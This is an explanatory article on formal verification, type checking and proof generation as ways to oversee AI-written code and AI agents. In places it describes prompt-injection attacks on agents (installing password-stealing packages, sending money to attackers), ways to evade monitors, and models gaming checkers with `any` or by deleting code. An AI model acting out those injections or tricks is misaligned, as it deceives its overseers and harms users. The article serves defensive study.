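# Formal methods and programming-language techniques for overseeing AI systems

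## What formal methods are and where they can be applied to AI

Formal methods are techniques that use mathematics to prove that a system obeys a stated rule, or to enforce that rule mechanically. Researchers have used them to build an operating-system kernel, a C compiler and a stack of cryptographic protocols. Most working programmers have never used them, mainly because they take so much work. The computer scientist Martin Kleppmann reports in *Prediction* (2025) that seL4, a small operating-system kernel, has 8,700 lines of C, and that its proof runs to 200,000 lines and took 20 person-years to write. He expects language models to make formal methods more worthwhile, because the models are getting good at writing proofs and because they also produce code that people would otherwise have to review by hand.

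Reviewing such code is a form of oversight, which here means people limiting or checking work they did not do and may not be able to follow. The obvious way to oversee an AI system is to have a person read its output or approve each risky step, but this quickly becomes unreliable. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) warn in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* that tired or overloaded reviewers approve unsafe actions. With a formal method, people write a rule once and a machine repeatedly checks that it is followed.

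One example can illustrate the whole subject. An online shop's payment program let a customer who paid 100 euros get two refunds of 60 euros each. The shop, whose owner cannot read code, gives the bug report to an AI agent. An agent is a learned model (a neural network whose behaviour comes from training rather than written instructions) that acts through tools. Each request it makes to run an outside function with given arguments is a tool call. This agent reads the report, searches the code, looks up the payment provider's documentation, rewrites the refund function, runs the tests and submits the change.

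### Specifications, tests and proofs

A specification is a precise statement of what a program must do or must never do. An everyday example from AWS, Amazon's cloud-computing company, is "data at rest on disk drives is always encrypted". A useful specification for the shop is that 0 ≤ refunded ≤ charged for every payment at all times. This excludes the bug, but it leaves out a great deal, since a program that refuses every refund also satisfies it.

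People disagree about how hard specifications are to write. Kleppmann thinks the specification is vastly easier than the proof. *The Specification Spectrum*, an essay on Imperial College London's website, says that a full specification of a messy real-world application is often longer and harder to write than the application itself. Both can be true, since they compare different things. The refund rule fits on one line because it doesn't describe the whole program.

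Programmers ordinarily look for the bug with a test, such as charging 100, refunding 60 twice, and checking whether the program refuses the second refund. They can also use a tool that generates thousands of random inputs and checks a general property each time. *The Specification Spectrum* illustrates this with a sorting function, where the property is that each number in the output is no larger than the next. But thousands of inputs can be a tiny fraction of the possibilities. Two 64-bit integers have 2¹²⁸ possible combinations, about 3.4 × 10³⁸, and a machine running a billion tests a second would need about 10²² years to try them all.

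A proof covers all of them at once by reasoning about the program's text. Suppose the agent's new refund function takes an amount r. If r > 0 and r ≤ charged − refunded, it pays out r and adds r to refunded; otherwise it refuses. At the start refunded is 0, so the rule that refunded ≤ charged holds. Now suppose the rule holds before some call. If the function refuses, nothing changes. If it pays, the new total is refunded + r, which is at most charged because r ≤ charged − refunded. The rule therefore holds after that call, and so after any number of calls with any amounts. A condition that stays true throughout a run is called an invariant.

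But the argument holds only if calls happen one at a time. If two refunds run at the same moment and both read the old total before either writes the new one, both pass the check and the customer gets 120 euros again. A guarantee's trusted computing base is everything that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold. Here it includes the database that keeps the calls separate, the compiler that turns the program into machine code, and the software that checked the proof. *The Specification Spectrum* makes a related criticism of verified software in general: the proved core still has to interact with unverified databases, caches and code for reading data formats.

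### What automatic checkers cannot do

A checker is sound if every program it accepts obeys the rule it checks, and complete if it accepts every program that obeys the rule. Soundness alone is easy to achieve, since a checker that rejects every program is sound.

For almost any rule about behaviour, no algorithm can have both properties and also always give an answer. This follows from a theorem that Henry Gordon Rice proved in his 1951 doctoral dissertation. The theorem applies to any property of what programs do when they run, rather than of their text, that some programs have and others lack. No algorithm can correctly decide, for every program, whether it has such a property.

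An example with refunds shows why. Suppose an algorithm could always tell whether a program ever refunds too much. For any program *a* and input *i*, we could write a program *t* that runs *a* on *i*, without letting *a* issue refunds itself, and then refunds twice what the customer was charged. *t* refunds too much exactly when *a* stops on *i*, because otherwise it never reaches the refund step. The algorithm could therefore determine whether *a* stops on *i* by checking *t*. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can do this for all programs and inputs.

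According to lecture notes from the University of Oregon, a program analysis can have at most two of three properties: being automatic, certain to finish, and exact. Most designers of automatic sound checkers give up exactness, so their tools reject some good programs. For example, a refund function might contain a line that would pay everything out twice, but only if a search finds positive whole numbers with a³ + b³ = c³. No such numbers exist, so the line never runs and the program is safe, but a checker without the number theory to prove this must still reject it. Designers can instead give up full automation and ask the programmer for annotations or a complete proof.

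Rice's theorem is less limiting in practice because it concerns arbitrary programs, and nobody has to accept every program. When a checker rejects a correct but convoluted refund function, the shop can tell the agent to write a plainer one, and an agent's time costs much less than a programmer's.

The checking described so far is static, meaning that it examines a program's text before the program runs. Dynamic checking examines a program while it runs. Tests are dynamic, and Møller and Schwartzbach (2024) note in *Static Program Analysis* that they can reveal errors but cannot show that there are none. A guard that runs in the live system is also dynamic, and it can do better than a test because it only has to check the current step. For example, it can refuse a request for 60 euros when only 40 are left. Rice's theorem does not rule this out. However, the guard has no information about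 later steps, so it may stop a job halfway through.

For agents, the choice often depends on whether a plan exists in advance. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) reviews 38 studies on specifying, verifying and enforcing what agents do. Fifteen cover checks made before the agent acts, but most of these checks need a finite workflow that is already laid out. Eight cover checks during the run, and six cover checks made only afterwards, when it is too late to prevent harm. The evidence is thin, and the review gives seven of the field's nine main claims its lowest rating for certainty.

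### Why a proof is easier to check than to find

A formal proof is easier to check than to find, just as confirming that 83 × 97 = 8,051 is easier than factoring 8,051 by hand. Every line of a proof must follow from earlier lines by one of a fixed list of rules, so a checker can verify each line in turn, and a proof twice as long takes very roughly twice the work. Finding a proof requires choosing a step at each line without knowing where it leads. Ten plausible choices at each of fifty lines make 10⁵⁰ candidates, of which the checker needs to check only one.

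Proofs are attractive for oversight because a machine can check them regardless of who wrote them, how they were written, or whether the writer was honest. If a language model makes up a step that does not follow, the checker rejects it and the model has to try again. Lean is software in which people or AI systems write proofs and a machine checks them. Its creator, Leo de Moura, told Lorica (2026) in *When AI Writes the Code, Who Proves It Works?* that trusting a Lean result means trusting only its kernel, the part that does the checking.

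People still have to read the statement of the theorem that was proved. AI Engineer (2026), in its notes on a conference talk, describes a project in which AI took about a week to convert zlib, a widely used compression library, into Lean. The specification is one line: decompress(compress(data)) = data. The proof is 32,000 lines long, and nobody needs to read it. But the theorem holds only for inputs smaller than one gibibyte. The plain-English requirement doesn't mention this limit, so an overseer who didn't read the theorem's statement would miss it.

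### Prompt injection and AgentDojo

The payment agent reads material that outsiders can write, including the bug report and the provider's documentation. Prompt injection is text in such material meant to make an agent follow someone else's instructions. For example, a web page could tell coding assistants to install a package that steals passwords. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues say the likely results for a software-engineering agent are insecure code, malicious packages, and company secrets leaked in a code change.

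*Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), attributes prompt injection to the technology itself, which "inherently does not distinguish" between instructions and data. SQL injection is an older attack in which an outsider slips commands into a database query, and programmers can stop it by keeping commands and data apart. The NCSC warns that prompt injection may never have so complete a remedy, a warning quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *UK NCSC Raises Alarms Over Prompt Injection Attacks*. In June 2026, a researcher from the software-security group OWASP still called it an "unresolved problem" (Poireault, 2026, *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*).

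Much of the research on defences against prompt injection uses one benchmark, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). *AgentDojo* has 97 tasks for agents in four simulated settings: an office workspace, Slack, a travel agency and a bank. The researchers paired each task with every attacker's goal in the same setting, which gave 629 security cases. In the bank, the user might ask the agent to pay a bill after an attacker has planted instructions in the data to send the attacker as much money as possible. Ordinary code then checks what happened in the simulated bank. The researchers avoided using a language model as judge because an injection that fools the agent might also fool the judge.

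AgentDojo measures three things: how many tasks the agent completes with no attack, how many it completes correctly under attack without harmful side effects, and how often the attacker achieves their goal. *SecOPD* (2026) uses a later, larger version of the benchmark with 949 cases. All the added cases are in the office workspace, which grew from 240 to 560, so average attack success rates from the two versions are not directly comparable.

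### Does the guarantee depend on the model?

*The Agent Knew* (2026) reports a test on AgentDojo in which researchers told agents not to obey instructions inside tool outputs. Attacks still succeeded 7.7% of the time with the model Gemma-4 and 26% of the time with gpt-oss. The safeguard was the same in both cases, but it depended on the model following the instruction, and Gemma-4 followed it more reliably than gpt-oss.

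Debenedetti and colleagues tested a filter on GPT-4o. Before reading any outside data, the agent chose the tools its task required, and it then lost access to the rest. Attacks succeeded 7.5% of the time, about the same rate as for Gemma-4 with its instruction. But the filter makes some attacks impossible, because an agent without an email tool cannot send email, whatever it reads. It cannot block attacks that need only the tools required for the task, which was true in 17% of the cases.

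Any safeguard can be tested by whether its guarantee holds for every output the model could produce or depends on how the model behaves. A guarantee that holds for every output is model-independent, so it still holds after a change of model, a bad training run or a successful prompt injection. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, explicitly design for model-independence. They trust the compiler, their own library and the runtime, along with an optional local model for secret material, and they treat the cloud model that drives the agent as a possible attacker. *Type-Checked Compliance* (2026), which describes a protocol for AI agents in finance, also assumes that the model is already compromised.

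Formal methods can be applied to the code an AI system writes, the actions it takes as an agent, or the computation inside its neural network. The payment bug involves all three.

The new refund function is ordinary code, so a sound checker can examine it just as it would examine code written by a person. The shop installs the change only if the checker proves that the amount refunded never exceeds the amount charged. This guarantee doesn't depend on the model that wrote the code, so it holds even if the model made mistakes or was hijacked. But it covers only the refund rule, so the same change could pass the check and still contain a line that sends out card numbers.

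Formal methods can also be applied to what an agent does while it works. A reference monitor is a component that every action must pass through and that can refuse it. Metere (2026), in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, gives a compact version. Let D be the set of permitted kinds of action, such as reading the code, running the tests and submitting a change for review. The monitor works out which kind each tool call belongs to, passes the call on if that kind is in D, and refuses it otherwise. Sending money is not in D, so the agent cannot send money. Metere does not analyse the model and treats it as an adversary that can emit anything. However many different texts the model can produce, the monitor can return only |D| + 1 verdicts, one for each permitted kind and one for refusal.

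But that count leaves out the arguments, and a permitted "submit a change" action can include a stolen password in its text. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues acknowledge a similar gap in agents that commit to a plan before reading outside data. An injection in someone's calendar can change the text of an email already in the plan, even though it cannot add a step.

The network's own computation is the hardest of the three places to apply formal methods. A neural network is also a program, a long series of arithmetic operations on its input and its weights (the numbers set during training), and researchers can prove some limited properties of networks. For the payment agent, we would like a proof that no bug report can lead it to request a transfer to a stranger. Someone would first have to define exactly which inputs count as bug reports and which outputs count as requests for such a transfer.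 The proof would also apply only to that particular model, so it would no longer hold after retraining.

Researchers can also monitor the network's internal states without proving anything. *The Agent Knew* used a readout of those states to block suspicious tool calls, which reduced attack success on gpt-oss from 28.5% to 17.5% with almost no loss of usefulness. That result covers only the attacks tested, and an attacker who knows about the readout can search for wording that gets past it.

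## Type systems for code written by language models

A type system is a set of rules for how programs may use values, and the compiler rejects programs that break them. It is the one formal method most programmers have used, since compiling a Java, Rust or TypeScript program includes checking its types. The check is automatic and usually quick.

### What a type checker does

Suppose the shop's agent works in TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with types, and writes a function that adds a new refund to the running total:

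```
function newTotal(refunded: number, r: number): number {
  return refunded + r;
}
```

The checker first records that `refunded` and `r` are numbers. This record is the type environment, which logicians write as Γ. The checker then looks up both names in Γ and applies its rule that adding two numbers gives a number. The result is written `Γ ⊢ refunded + r : number`, which means that the expression has type number in the environment Γ. That matches the declared return type, so the function passes.

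Suppose another part of the program calls `newTotal(60, amount)`, where `amount` is text that a customer typed into a web form. JavaScript would join the two values instead of adding them, so 60 and "60" would give "6060". The checker rejects the call because the function requires a number and `amount` is a string. It does this without running the program, so what the customer typed makes no difference.

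We can rely on such a check if the type system is sound. Robin Milner proved a soundness theorem in 1978 and summed it up in the slogan that well-typed programs cannot "go wrong". Most proofs now follow a method that Andrew Wright and Matthias Felleisen published in 1994. They treat a run as a series of small steps, so that (100 − 60) + 5 becomes 40 + 5 and then 45. In its usual modern form, the proof has two parts:

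- **Progress:** a well-typed program has either finished or can take another step.
- **Preservation:** if a well-typed program takes a step, the result is also well typed, with the same type.

A well-typed program that has not finished can take a step (progress), and the result is also well typed (preservation), so the same reasoning applies to every later step. The program therefore never gets stuck in a meaningless state, such as trying to call the number 40 as a function, though it may still run forever or compute the wrong number. Researchers often prove this soundness theorem only for a small core of a language, as *ETAS* (2026) does for a new language for writing agent systems. TypeScript as a whole is not sound, because its designers deliberately left ways around the checker.

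### Stronger types and what they cost

Simple types like these take little effort to use. Programmers annotate the inputs and outputs of functions, and the compiler infers most of the rest. But these types don't distinguish a refund of 6,000 euros from a refund of 60, because both are numbers.

Rust's ownership rules add memory safety. In C, a program can release a piece of memory and then keep using it, which attackers can exploit. In Rust, every value has one owner, and the program releases the value when its owner goes out of scope. Other code can borrow the value through many read-only references or a single reference that allows changes, but not both at the same time.

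*Generative Compilation* (Mündler-Sasahara, Venev and colleagues, 2026) gives an example of a mistake a model might make when stripping a header from a message. The code makes `tag` refer to the first few bytes of the message, deletes those bytes, and then reads `tag`. Rust's compiler rejects this because the message changes while `tag` is still borrowing from it. The fix is to copy the header before deleting it. Rust's ownership rules require few extra annotations, but programmers sometimes have to add copies or redesign their data to satisfy them.

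Refinement types attach a condition to an ordinary type. The shop could require that the argument of its payout function be a number r with 0 < r ≤ charged − refunded. At each call, the type checker queries an SMT solver, a program that decides whether certain logical formulas can be satisfied. The solver searches for a value of r that could reach the call and break the condition. If the call is inside an `if` that tests the condition, no such value exists and the code compiles. Without the `if`, the solver finds one, such as r = 6,000, and the code doesn't compile. Somebody has to write these conditions, often including an invariant for each loop, and the solver can fail on harder arithmetic.

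Dependent types can refer to values. In an example from *The Specification Spectrum*, the type of a matrix multiplication function requires the first matrix to have as many columns as the second has rows. Such types can express almost any mathematical statement about a program, and Lean uses them for this. But a person or an AI system often has to supply a proof before the program will compile. Types can also record which files and services a piece of code may use, as in the TACIT system that Odersky and colleagues built for agents.

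### Checking types while the model writes

A language model writes code one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. At each step it assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the software around it picks one according to those probabilities. An ordinary compiler can't help at this stage because it checks only complete programs.

In *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models*, Mündler, He and colleagues (2025) built a type checker for incomplete programs. A partial program is acceptable if some continuation would make it a well-typed program. The software picks a token and tests whether the program so far, plus that token, is still acceptable. If not, it sets the token's probability to zero, rescales the other probabilities and picks again.

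In one of their examples, the partial code ends at `parseInt(num`, where `num` is a number but `parseInt` requires a string. CodeLlama 34B continued with `, 10)`, which doesn't compile because `num` is still a number. The constrained version blocks this continuation, and the model writes `.toString()` instead, which converts the number to a string. The software checks whether a string is still reachable by searching a graph whose nodes are types and whose edges are operations. From "number", the member `toString` leads to "function returning a string", and calling that function leads to "string". The graph can be infinite, so the search skips very complicated types. This makes it reject some valid programs, but it never accepts partial code that can't be completed with correct types.

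Mündler and colleagues tested six open-weight models on TypeScript versions of two sets of short programming problems, HumanEval and MBPP. Enforcing type rules as the models wrote or translated functions reduced compile errors by 75.3% on HumanEval and 52.1% on MBPP. Enforcing only grammar would have removed at most 9.0% and 4.9%. Correctness, measured by unit tests, rose much less, by 3.5% in relative terms for writing new functions and 5.0% for translation. With the smallest model, Gemma 2 2B, failures to compile on HumanEval fell from 103 to 44 out of 636 attempts, but only about seven more programs passed their tests. With Qwen2.5 32B, a stronger model, 15 of the 21 programs that compiled only with type enforcement were correct.

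These figures come from a set-up that favours the constraint, because Mündler and colleagues kept every program that compiled without it and used it only to regenerate those that failed. Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026), in *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, applied the constraint from the start with the same six models. The models wrote significantly more correct programs without the constraint in 22 of 24 comparisons. For example, Qwen2.5 32B solved 82.3% of HumanEval without it and 72.3% with it.

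The cause was valid code that the checker could not handle. In one task, Gemma 2 2B started to write a call to `isPalindrome`, a function to be defined further down the file. TypeScript allows this, but the constrained checker doesn't. The model had already written "is", so it ended up with `isNaN`, an existing function that tests for something else, and the program was well typed but wrong. The constrained checker would have rejected 982 of the 4,231 programs by this model that compiled normally. Biagiola and colleagues also tested a simple configuration language, TOML, with a checker that accepted every valid file. In that test, the constraint improved correctness by 2.5% for a 32B model and by up to 54% for a 2B one.

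Constrained decoding also needs the model's token probabilities, which companies often don't release for their best models. Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues avoid this need by checking unfinished code with the normal Rust compiler. Their software closes open brackets, fills gaps with placeholders that fit any type, and compiles the result. If compilation fails, the model receives the error message and starts again. They designed the method never to reject a beginning that could still become a valid program, and proved this in Lean for a small Rust-like language. The method may take a while to detect that a beginning can't become a valid program, but the compiler still checks the finished file.

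In a test of seven models on difficult Rust tasks, 65.9% of outputs failed to compile when the models received no feedback. Returning compiler errors on finished files reduced this to 20.7%, and checking the code as the model wrote it reduced it to 13.1%. Most of the benefit therefore comes from the ordinary loop in which a model writes a file, reads the compiler's errors and tries again.

### Translating C to Rust

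Much of the world's critical software is in C, and people are now using AI to move some of it to Rust. The *TRACTOR* programme at DARPA, the US defence research agency, aims to automate this at the quality of a skilled Rust developer. A translation can compile and still behave differently from the original. In translation tests by Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues, only 2.6% of translations by Claude Opus 4.8 with early feedback failed to compile, but only 62.3% passed their tests. It is also harder to produce idiomatic translations, written the way Rust programmers normally write. *SACTOR* (2026) reports an average success rate of 85% on a 50-program sample for plain translations, but 52% for idiomatic ones.

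Wang, Paulsen and colleagues (2026), in *Mostly Automatic Translation of Language Interpreters from C to Safe Rust*, translated six larger programs. All were interpreters (programs that run code in languages such as JavaScript), each with 6,000 to 23,000 lines of C. Agents first removed features from the C program until it did little more than print a piece of text. They translated that version, then restored the features one group at a time, testing at every stage. Each translation took 28 to 90 hours, cost $460 to $1,780, and needed one to eleven short human interventions. All six translations passed every test the agents had been given, but only 62% to 92% of the tests the researchers had withheld.

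The memory-safety results were better. Wang and colleagues put 20 old security holes back into the JavaScript interpreter before translating it, and the memory errors among them disappeared in the Rust version. They warn that the model may have remembered some published fixes. That possibility matters less for memory errors than for other bugs, because Rust's rules would exclude most memory errors anyway.

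The best long-term evidence comes from Android, though the comparison isn't about AI. *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reports that memory-safety bugs fell below 20% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2025 for the first time. Google had found one potential memory-safety vulnerability in about 5 million lines of Rust, and fixed it before release. The historical rate for C and C++ in Android was about 1,000 per million lines. Some of that gap may reflect age, since the Rust is mostly new and people have had much longer to find bugs in the older code, but age is unlikely to explain a more than thousandfold difference.

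### Ways around the checker

Most practical languages let programmers bypass the type system. In TypeScript, giving a value the type `any` switches off checking for it, and a cast makes the compiler assume a type that the value may not have. Many languages also offer reflection, which lets a program look up functions by name while it runs, so the checker can't tell in advance which function will be called. Rust has `unsafe` blocks for operations such as using raw memory addresses. Most of the compiler's safety checks stay on inside these blocks, according to Vander Stoep, who calls it a common misconception that `unsafe` disables them. *LLM4C2Rust* (2026) describes `unsafe` that way.

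These escape hatches have legitimate uses. *AgenticTyper* (2026) uses agents to add types to old JavaScript projects. Some working code can't be given a type without changing its behavior, so the agents insert a comment that suppresses the error. If the error reveals a real bug, the comment marks it for a person to review.

Rewarding a model simply for passing the checker is dangerous because replacing every difficult type with `any` earns the same reward as fixing the code and is much easier. Indirect evidence suggests that such a reward can do harm. Biagiola and colleagues trained two models with a reward of 1 for each program that passed their type checker and 0 for any other. On HumanEval, the share of programs generated without the constraint that passed this checker rose from 72% to 92%. But the smaller model's correctness without the constraint fell by 3.7 percentage points, which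 they attribute to the reward favouring programs that were well typed but wrong. The larger model's correctness stayed about the same. They did not report whether either model used escape hatches.

One remedy is to ban escape hatches in AI-written code. A short script can reject any file that contains `any`, a cast or a suppression comment, and one line in a Rust package can make the compiler reject `unsafe` blocks in that package. The agent must not be able to edit the script or the compiler's settings.

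In TypeScript, a ban means the agent has to write extra code to check data from outside the program, and it may have to restructure old code that has no suitable type. In Rust, a ban makes some work impossible. About 4% of Android's Rust is inside `unsafe` blocks, and Vander Stoep says a ban is "not workable" for an operating system, which has to control hardware and call C code. Wang and colleagues banned `unsafe` because subtle memory errors in such code are hard to detect automatically. This ruled out programs that generate machine code as they run.

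One compromise is to have experts write the few unsafe operations in a small library and restrict agents to safe code that calls it. The trusted computing base then includes the library and any unsafe code in other packages the program uses. A program can use many packages. A commenter on Ubuntu's *An update on rust-coreutils* counted 523 entries in one project's package list.

### What well-typed code can still do wrong

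If the agent writes `refunded - r` instead of `refunded + r`, the function still returns a number and passes the simple type checker. The recorded total then goes down with each refund, so the customer can keep asking for more.

Experienced programmers also make mistakes that types miss. The project with 523 entries is uutils, a Rust rewrite of the basic Linux commands for copying, moving and deleting files. Ubuntu, a widely used version of Linux, commissioned a security audit of uutils that found 113 issues. corrode's *Bugs Rust Won't Catch* reviews the 44 vulnerabilities that Ubuntu's developer, Canonical, disclosed in April 2026. None was a buffer overflow or a use of released memory, though both have occurred in the older C versions.

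Many of the bugs came from wrong assumptions about the world outside the program. The command for changing file permissions had a safeguard against changing the whole disk, but it only checked whether the user had typed "/", so "/../", which means the same place, got past it. The command for installing files deleted the old file and then created a new one under the same name. Between the two steps, an attacker could put a link to the system's password file under that name, and the command would overwrite the password file. Because of similar bugs, Ubuntu 26.04 still uses the C versions of the copy, move and delete commands. The shop's refund function has the same weakness when two refunds run at once, even if every line is well typed.

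## Proving that AI-written programs meet their specifications

To rule out a mistake like the refund function's misplaced minus sign, someone has to state which number the function should return and then prove that it always returns that number. Computer scientists worked out how to do this in the late 1960s. Few people wrote such proofs because they took so much work, but language models now write many of them.

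### Hoare triples and a worked loop

Tony Hoare published the standard notation for such proofs in 1969, two years after Robert Floyd introduced a similar method for flowcharts. A Hoare triple has the form {P} C {Q}, where C is a piece of code, the precondition P is a condition on the program's state before C runs, and the postcondition Q is a condition on its state afterwards. The triple holds if, whenever P is true at the start and C finishes, Q is true at the end. For example, {refunded = 60} refunded := refunded + 5 {refunded = 65} holds, but it would not hold if the code subtracted 5 instead.

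Each kind of statement has its own rule. For an assignment x := e, we find the precondition by replacing every x in the postcondition with e. If refunded ≤ 100 must be true after refunded := refunded + r, then refunded + r ≤ 100 must be true beforehand. The shop's buggy program never checked that condition.

Loops need more thought because the same lines can run any number of times. This program adds up the whole numbers from 1 to n:

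```
s := 0
i := 0
while i < n:
    i := i + 1
    s := s + i
```

The precondition is n ≥ 0 and the postcondition is s = n(n + 1)/2. With n = 4, for instance, the program should return 1 + 2 + 3 + 4 = 10, which is 4 × 5/2. The proof needs an invariant, and a suitable one is "s = i(i + 1)/2 and i ≤ n". It leaves three things to prove, known as proof obligations:

- Start: the invariant is true before the loop begins. Both s and i are 0, and 0 = 0 × 1/2. The precondition gives 0 ≤ n.
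- Step: if the invariant is true and the loop goes round once more, it is still true. The loop continues only if i < n, so the new value i + 1 is at most n. The new total is i(i + 1)/2 + (i + 1), which equals (i + 1)(i + 2)/2. That is the formula in the invariant with i + 1 in place of i.
- Exit: when the loop stops, the postcondition is true. The loop stops only when i < n is false, so i ≥ n. The invariant gives i ≤ n. Therefore i = n, and s = n(n + 1)/2.

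These obligations show that if the loop stops, the answer is right. To show that it does stop, we need a quantity that shrinks on every iteration but can't shrink forever. Here n − i falls by one each time and never goes below zero.

The proof needs the condition i ≤ n, even though it looks too obvious to mention. Without it, we would know only that i ≥ n when the loop exits, which allows n = 3, i = 5 and s = 15. The program would still be correct, but we would be unable to prove it. Most of the skill in verifying loops is finding an invariant that every iteration preserves and that is strong enough to prove the specification at the exit. The rest of the proof is often routine algebra.

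### Two routes to a proof

One approach, used by Dafny, a programming language designed for verification, and Verus, a tool for verifying Rust programs, is to leave the algebra to an SMT solver. In Dafny, the programmer writes `requires n >= 0` and `ensures s == n * (n + 1) / 2` at the top of the function and puts the invariant next to the loop. Dafny applies rules like Hoare's to turn the annotated program into proof obligations. The solver looks for a counterexample to each one, as it does for refinement types. If it finds one or stops without an answer, Dafny reports an error at the corresponding line.

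The solver often needs hints. According to Dafny's *The Cost of Bugs and of Verification* (2025), programmers still have to write loop invariants, intermediate assertions and "decreases" clauses (which name the quantity that shrinks at each step), and most developers have never learned the logic involved. The Dafny team therefore proposed dafny-annotator, which combines a language model with a search procedure to add the hints automatically.

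A verifier for ordinary programming languages also has to account for machine limits, such as the maximum size of an integer. Dafny's standard integers are unbounded, but a signed 32-bit integer in Rust cannot exceed 2,147,483,647, and the sum from 1 to 65,536 is 2,147,516,416. If the loop used signed 32-bit integers, Verus would reject it until the programmer added a precondition that n is at most 65,535.

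The other route uses a proof assistant, such as Lean or Rocq (formerly called Coq). The user states a theorem and enters commands called tactics. After each tactic, the proof assistant displays what is left to prove. For the sum, one tactic starts an induction on n, which splits the problem into the case n = 0 and the step from n to n + 1. Another tactic does the algebra.

Proof assistants can handle theorems that are far too hard for a solver, such as the correctness of a whole compiler, and they require trusting much less software. But somebody has to find the steps of the proof. CompCert, a C compiler verified in Rocq, took about three person-years and 42,000 lines of Rocq, according to *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026).

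### How a model writes a proof

In both routes, a person supplies the specification, a language model writes the code and a proof or annotations, and the checker returns errors until the model has fixed them all.

Suppose a model receives the specification of the sum program and writes the loop with the invariant `s == i * (i + 1) / 2` but omits `i <= n`. Dafny reports that the postcondition might not hold. In response, the model adds the missing invariant, because without it Dafny cannot rule out that `i` exceeds `n`. Dafny then accepts the program. A failed proof obligation can mean that the proof is too weak or that the program is wrong, so a different error might have led the model to fix the code instead.

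The software that runs this loop must stop the model from changing the specification and reject commands that let a proof skip a step, such as `assume` in Dafny and `sorry` in Lean. With those precautions, wrong guesses waste only time and money. Kleppmann says he would take AI-generated code with a proof over handwritten code with its bugs.

In *A benchmark for vericoding*, Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025) measured how well that year's models could generate verified code from a formal specification, which they call "vericoding". They contrast it with vibe coding, where a person describes the program in plain language and gets code that may contain bugs. The benchmark has 12,504 specifications, of which 6,174 were new.

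| Language | Specifications | Success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Dafny | 3,029 | 82% |
| Verus/Rust | 2,334 | 44% |
| Lean | 7,141 | 27% |

Models probably score low in Lean because they have to write much more of the proof themselves. The scores for the three languages aren't directly comparable, though, because each language had a different number of problems. Adding a description in plain language made no significant difference. Bursuc and colleagues found that the best success rate on the narrower task of verifying Dafny programs, where the model doesn't have to write the code, had risen from 68% to 96% in a year.

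Those scores are now out of date. Researchers still use the benchmark, and the thesis *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (May 2026) pairs it with Dalek Bench, in which a model must complete or repair Lean proofs inside an existing project. But most benchmark problems are short, self-contained functions, so real software provides better evidence about recent models.

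That evidence shows people handing more and more of the proof to AI. An early report, Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It*, describes Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, completing many complex steps in a proof assistant with a human expert as its "project manager". Slides from Lean (2026) describe a 39,000-line proof about Move, a language for programs that run on blockchains. Claude repaired broken proofs and handled routine cases, but people were still needed for new proof strategies. The slides also describe a Google project in which developers attach Lean specifications to `unsafe` Rust. In a demonstration, an agent wrote `unsafe` code and proved it sound, so work on code that Rust's own checker can't verify may not have to be left to human experts.

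### Turning fuzz tests into theorems

The largest test so far appeared in October 2026. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes a collaboration with Theorem, a verification start-up, in which Claude proved security properties of 123 open-source libraries. The project took a few weeks, according to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026).

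The researchers reused fuzz tests as specifications for the 123 libraries, which took far less time than writing specifications by hand would have. Fuzzing means running a program on huge numbers of random or mutated inputs to see whether it crashes. Google's OSS-Fuzz project continuously fuzzes open-source software, and its libraries already come with small test programs for this. Each test program takes a string of bytes, passes it to some of the library's functions and stops. Its author expects that no input will make it crash, and that expectation can serve as a specification.

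*Pre-QED* (Lim, Tu and colleagues, 2026) explains how the system turns the expectation into a theorem. The system first compiles the library and the fuzz test into a single program for RISC-V, a processor design with a simple instruction set. The compiler inserts extra checks, called sanitizers, that make the program crash when it reads or writes memory it shouldn't. Without them, such an error could corrupt data without stopping the program.

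The system then combines the program with a mathematical model of the processor and of Linux. For every instruction, the model specifies how the registers and memory change. From these parts, the system automatically generates a theorem of roughly this form:

*For every input smaller than 64 MB, every response that the modelled operating system can give, and every layout of memory, the program ends normally.*

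"Normally" excludes memory errors and failed assertions. Some fuzz tests also compress data, decompress it and deliberately crash if the result differs from the original. For those tests, the same theorem guarantees that decompression returns the original data.

Claude wrote the proofs in Rocq, whose kernel checked them. Loops in machine code also need invariants, like the one for the sum, but these invariants concern registers and addresses. For example, a certain register might always point inside the input.

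A Russian news report, OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), puts the proofs at about 180 million lines of Rocq in total, or around 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 instructions. That is 33 lines of proof per instruction, while seL4 has about 23 lines of proof per line of C, and CompCert's proofs are eight times as long as the compiler, according to Dafny. Since one line of C usually compiles to several instructions, the gap is wider when measured per instruction. Longer proofs also take more tokens to generate, and Lim and colleagues list token use among the things that must come down before verification becomes routine.

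### Bugs found while proving

Claude succeeded for 239 fuzz tests and found hundreds of bugs along the way. Looking for a proof is a good way to find bugs because the prover must account for every case. When an obligation is hard to prove, the prover can look for an input that violates it, and sometimes one exists. OpenNET mentions a buffer overflow in libexpat, a widely used library for reading XML files. Other bugs appear only with inputs of tens of megabytes, which fuzzers rarely try because small inputs let them run many more tests.

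When Claude found a bug, it patched the library. The system then generated a new theorem for the patched program, and Claude tried again. Allowing patches creates an incentive to cheat, since deleting most of a function is an easy way to stop it from crashing. The researchers penalised patches, gave extra credit for proving which inputs a patch affected, and logged every patch for audit.

Some of the 239 theorems therefore concern patched versions of the libraries, not the versions people had installed. EconoTimes reports that Anthropic is publishing proofs for programs that needed no changes, along with specifications that Claude could not prove, and has invited others to check the work. The figure of 239 does not include these failed attempts.

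### What the 239 theorems cover

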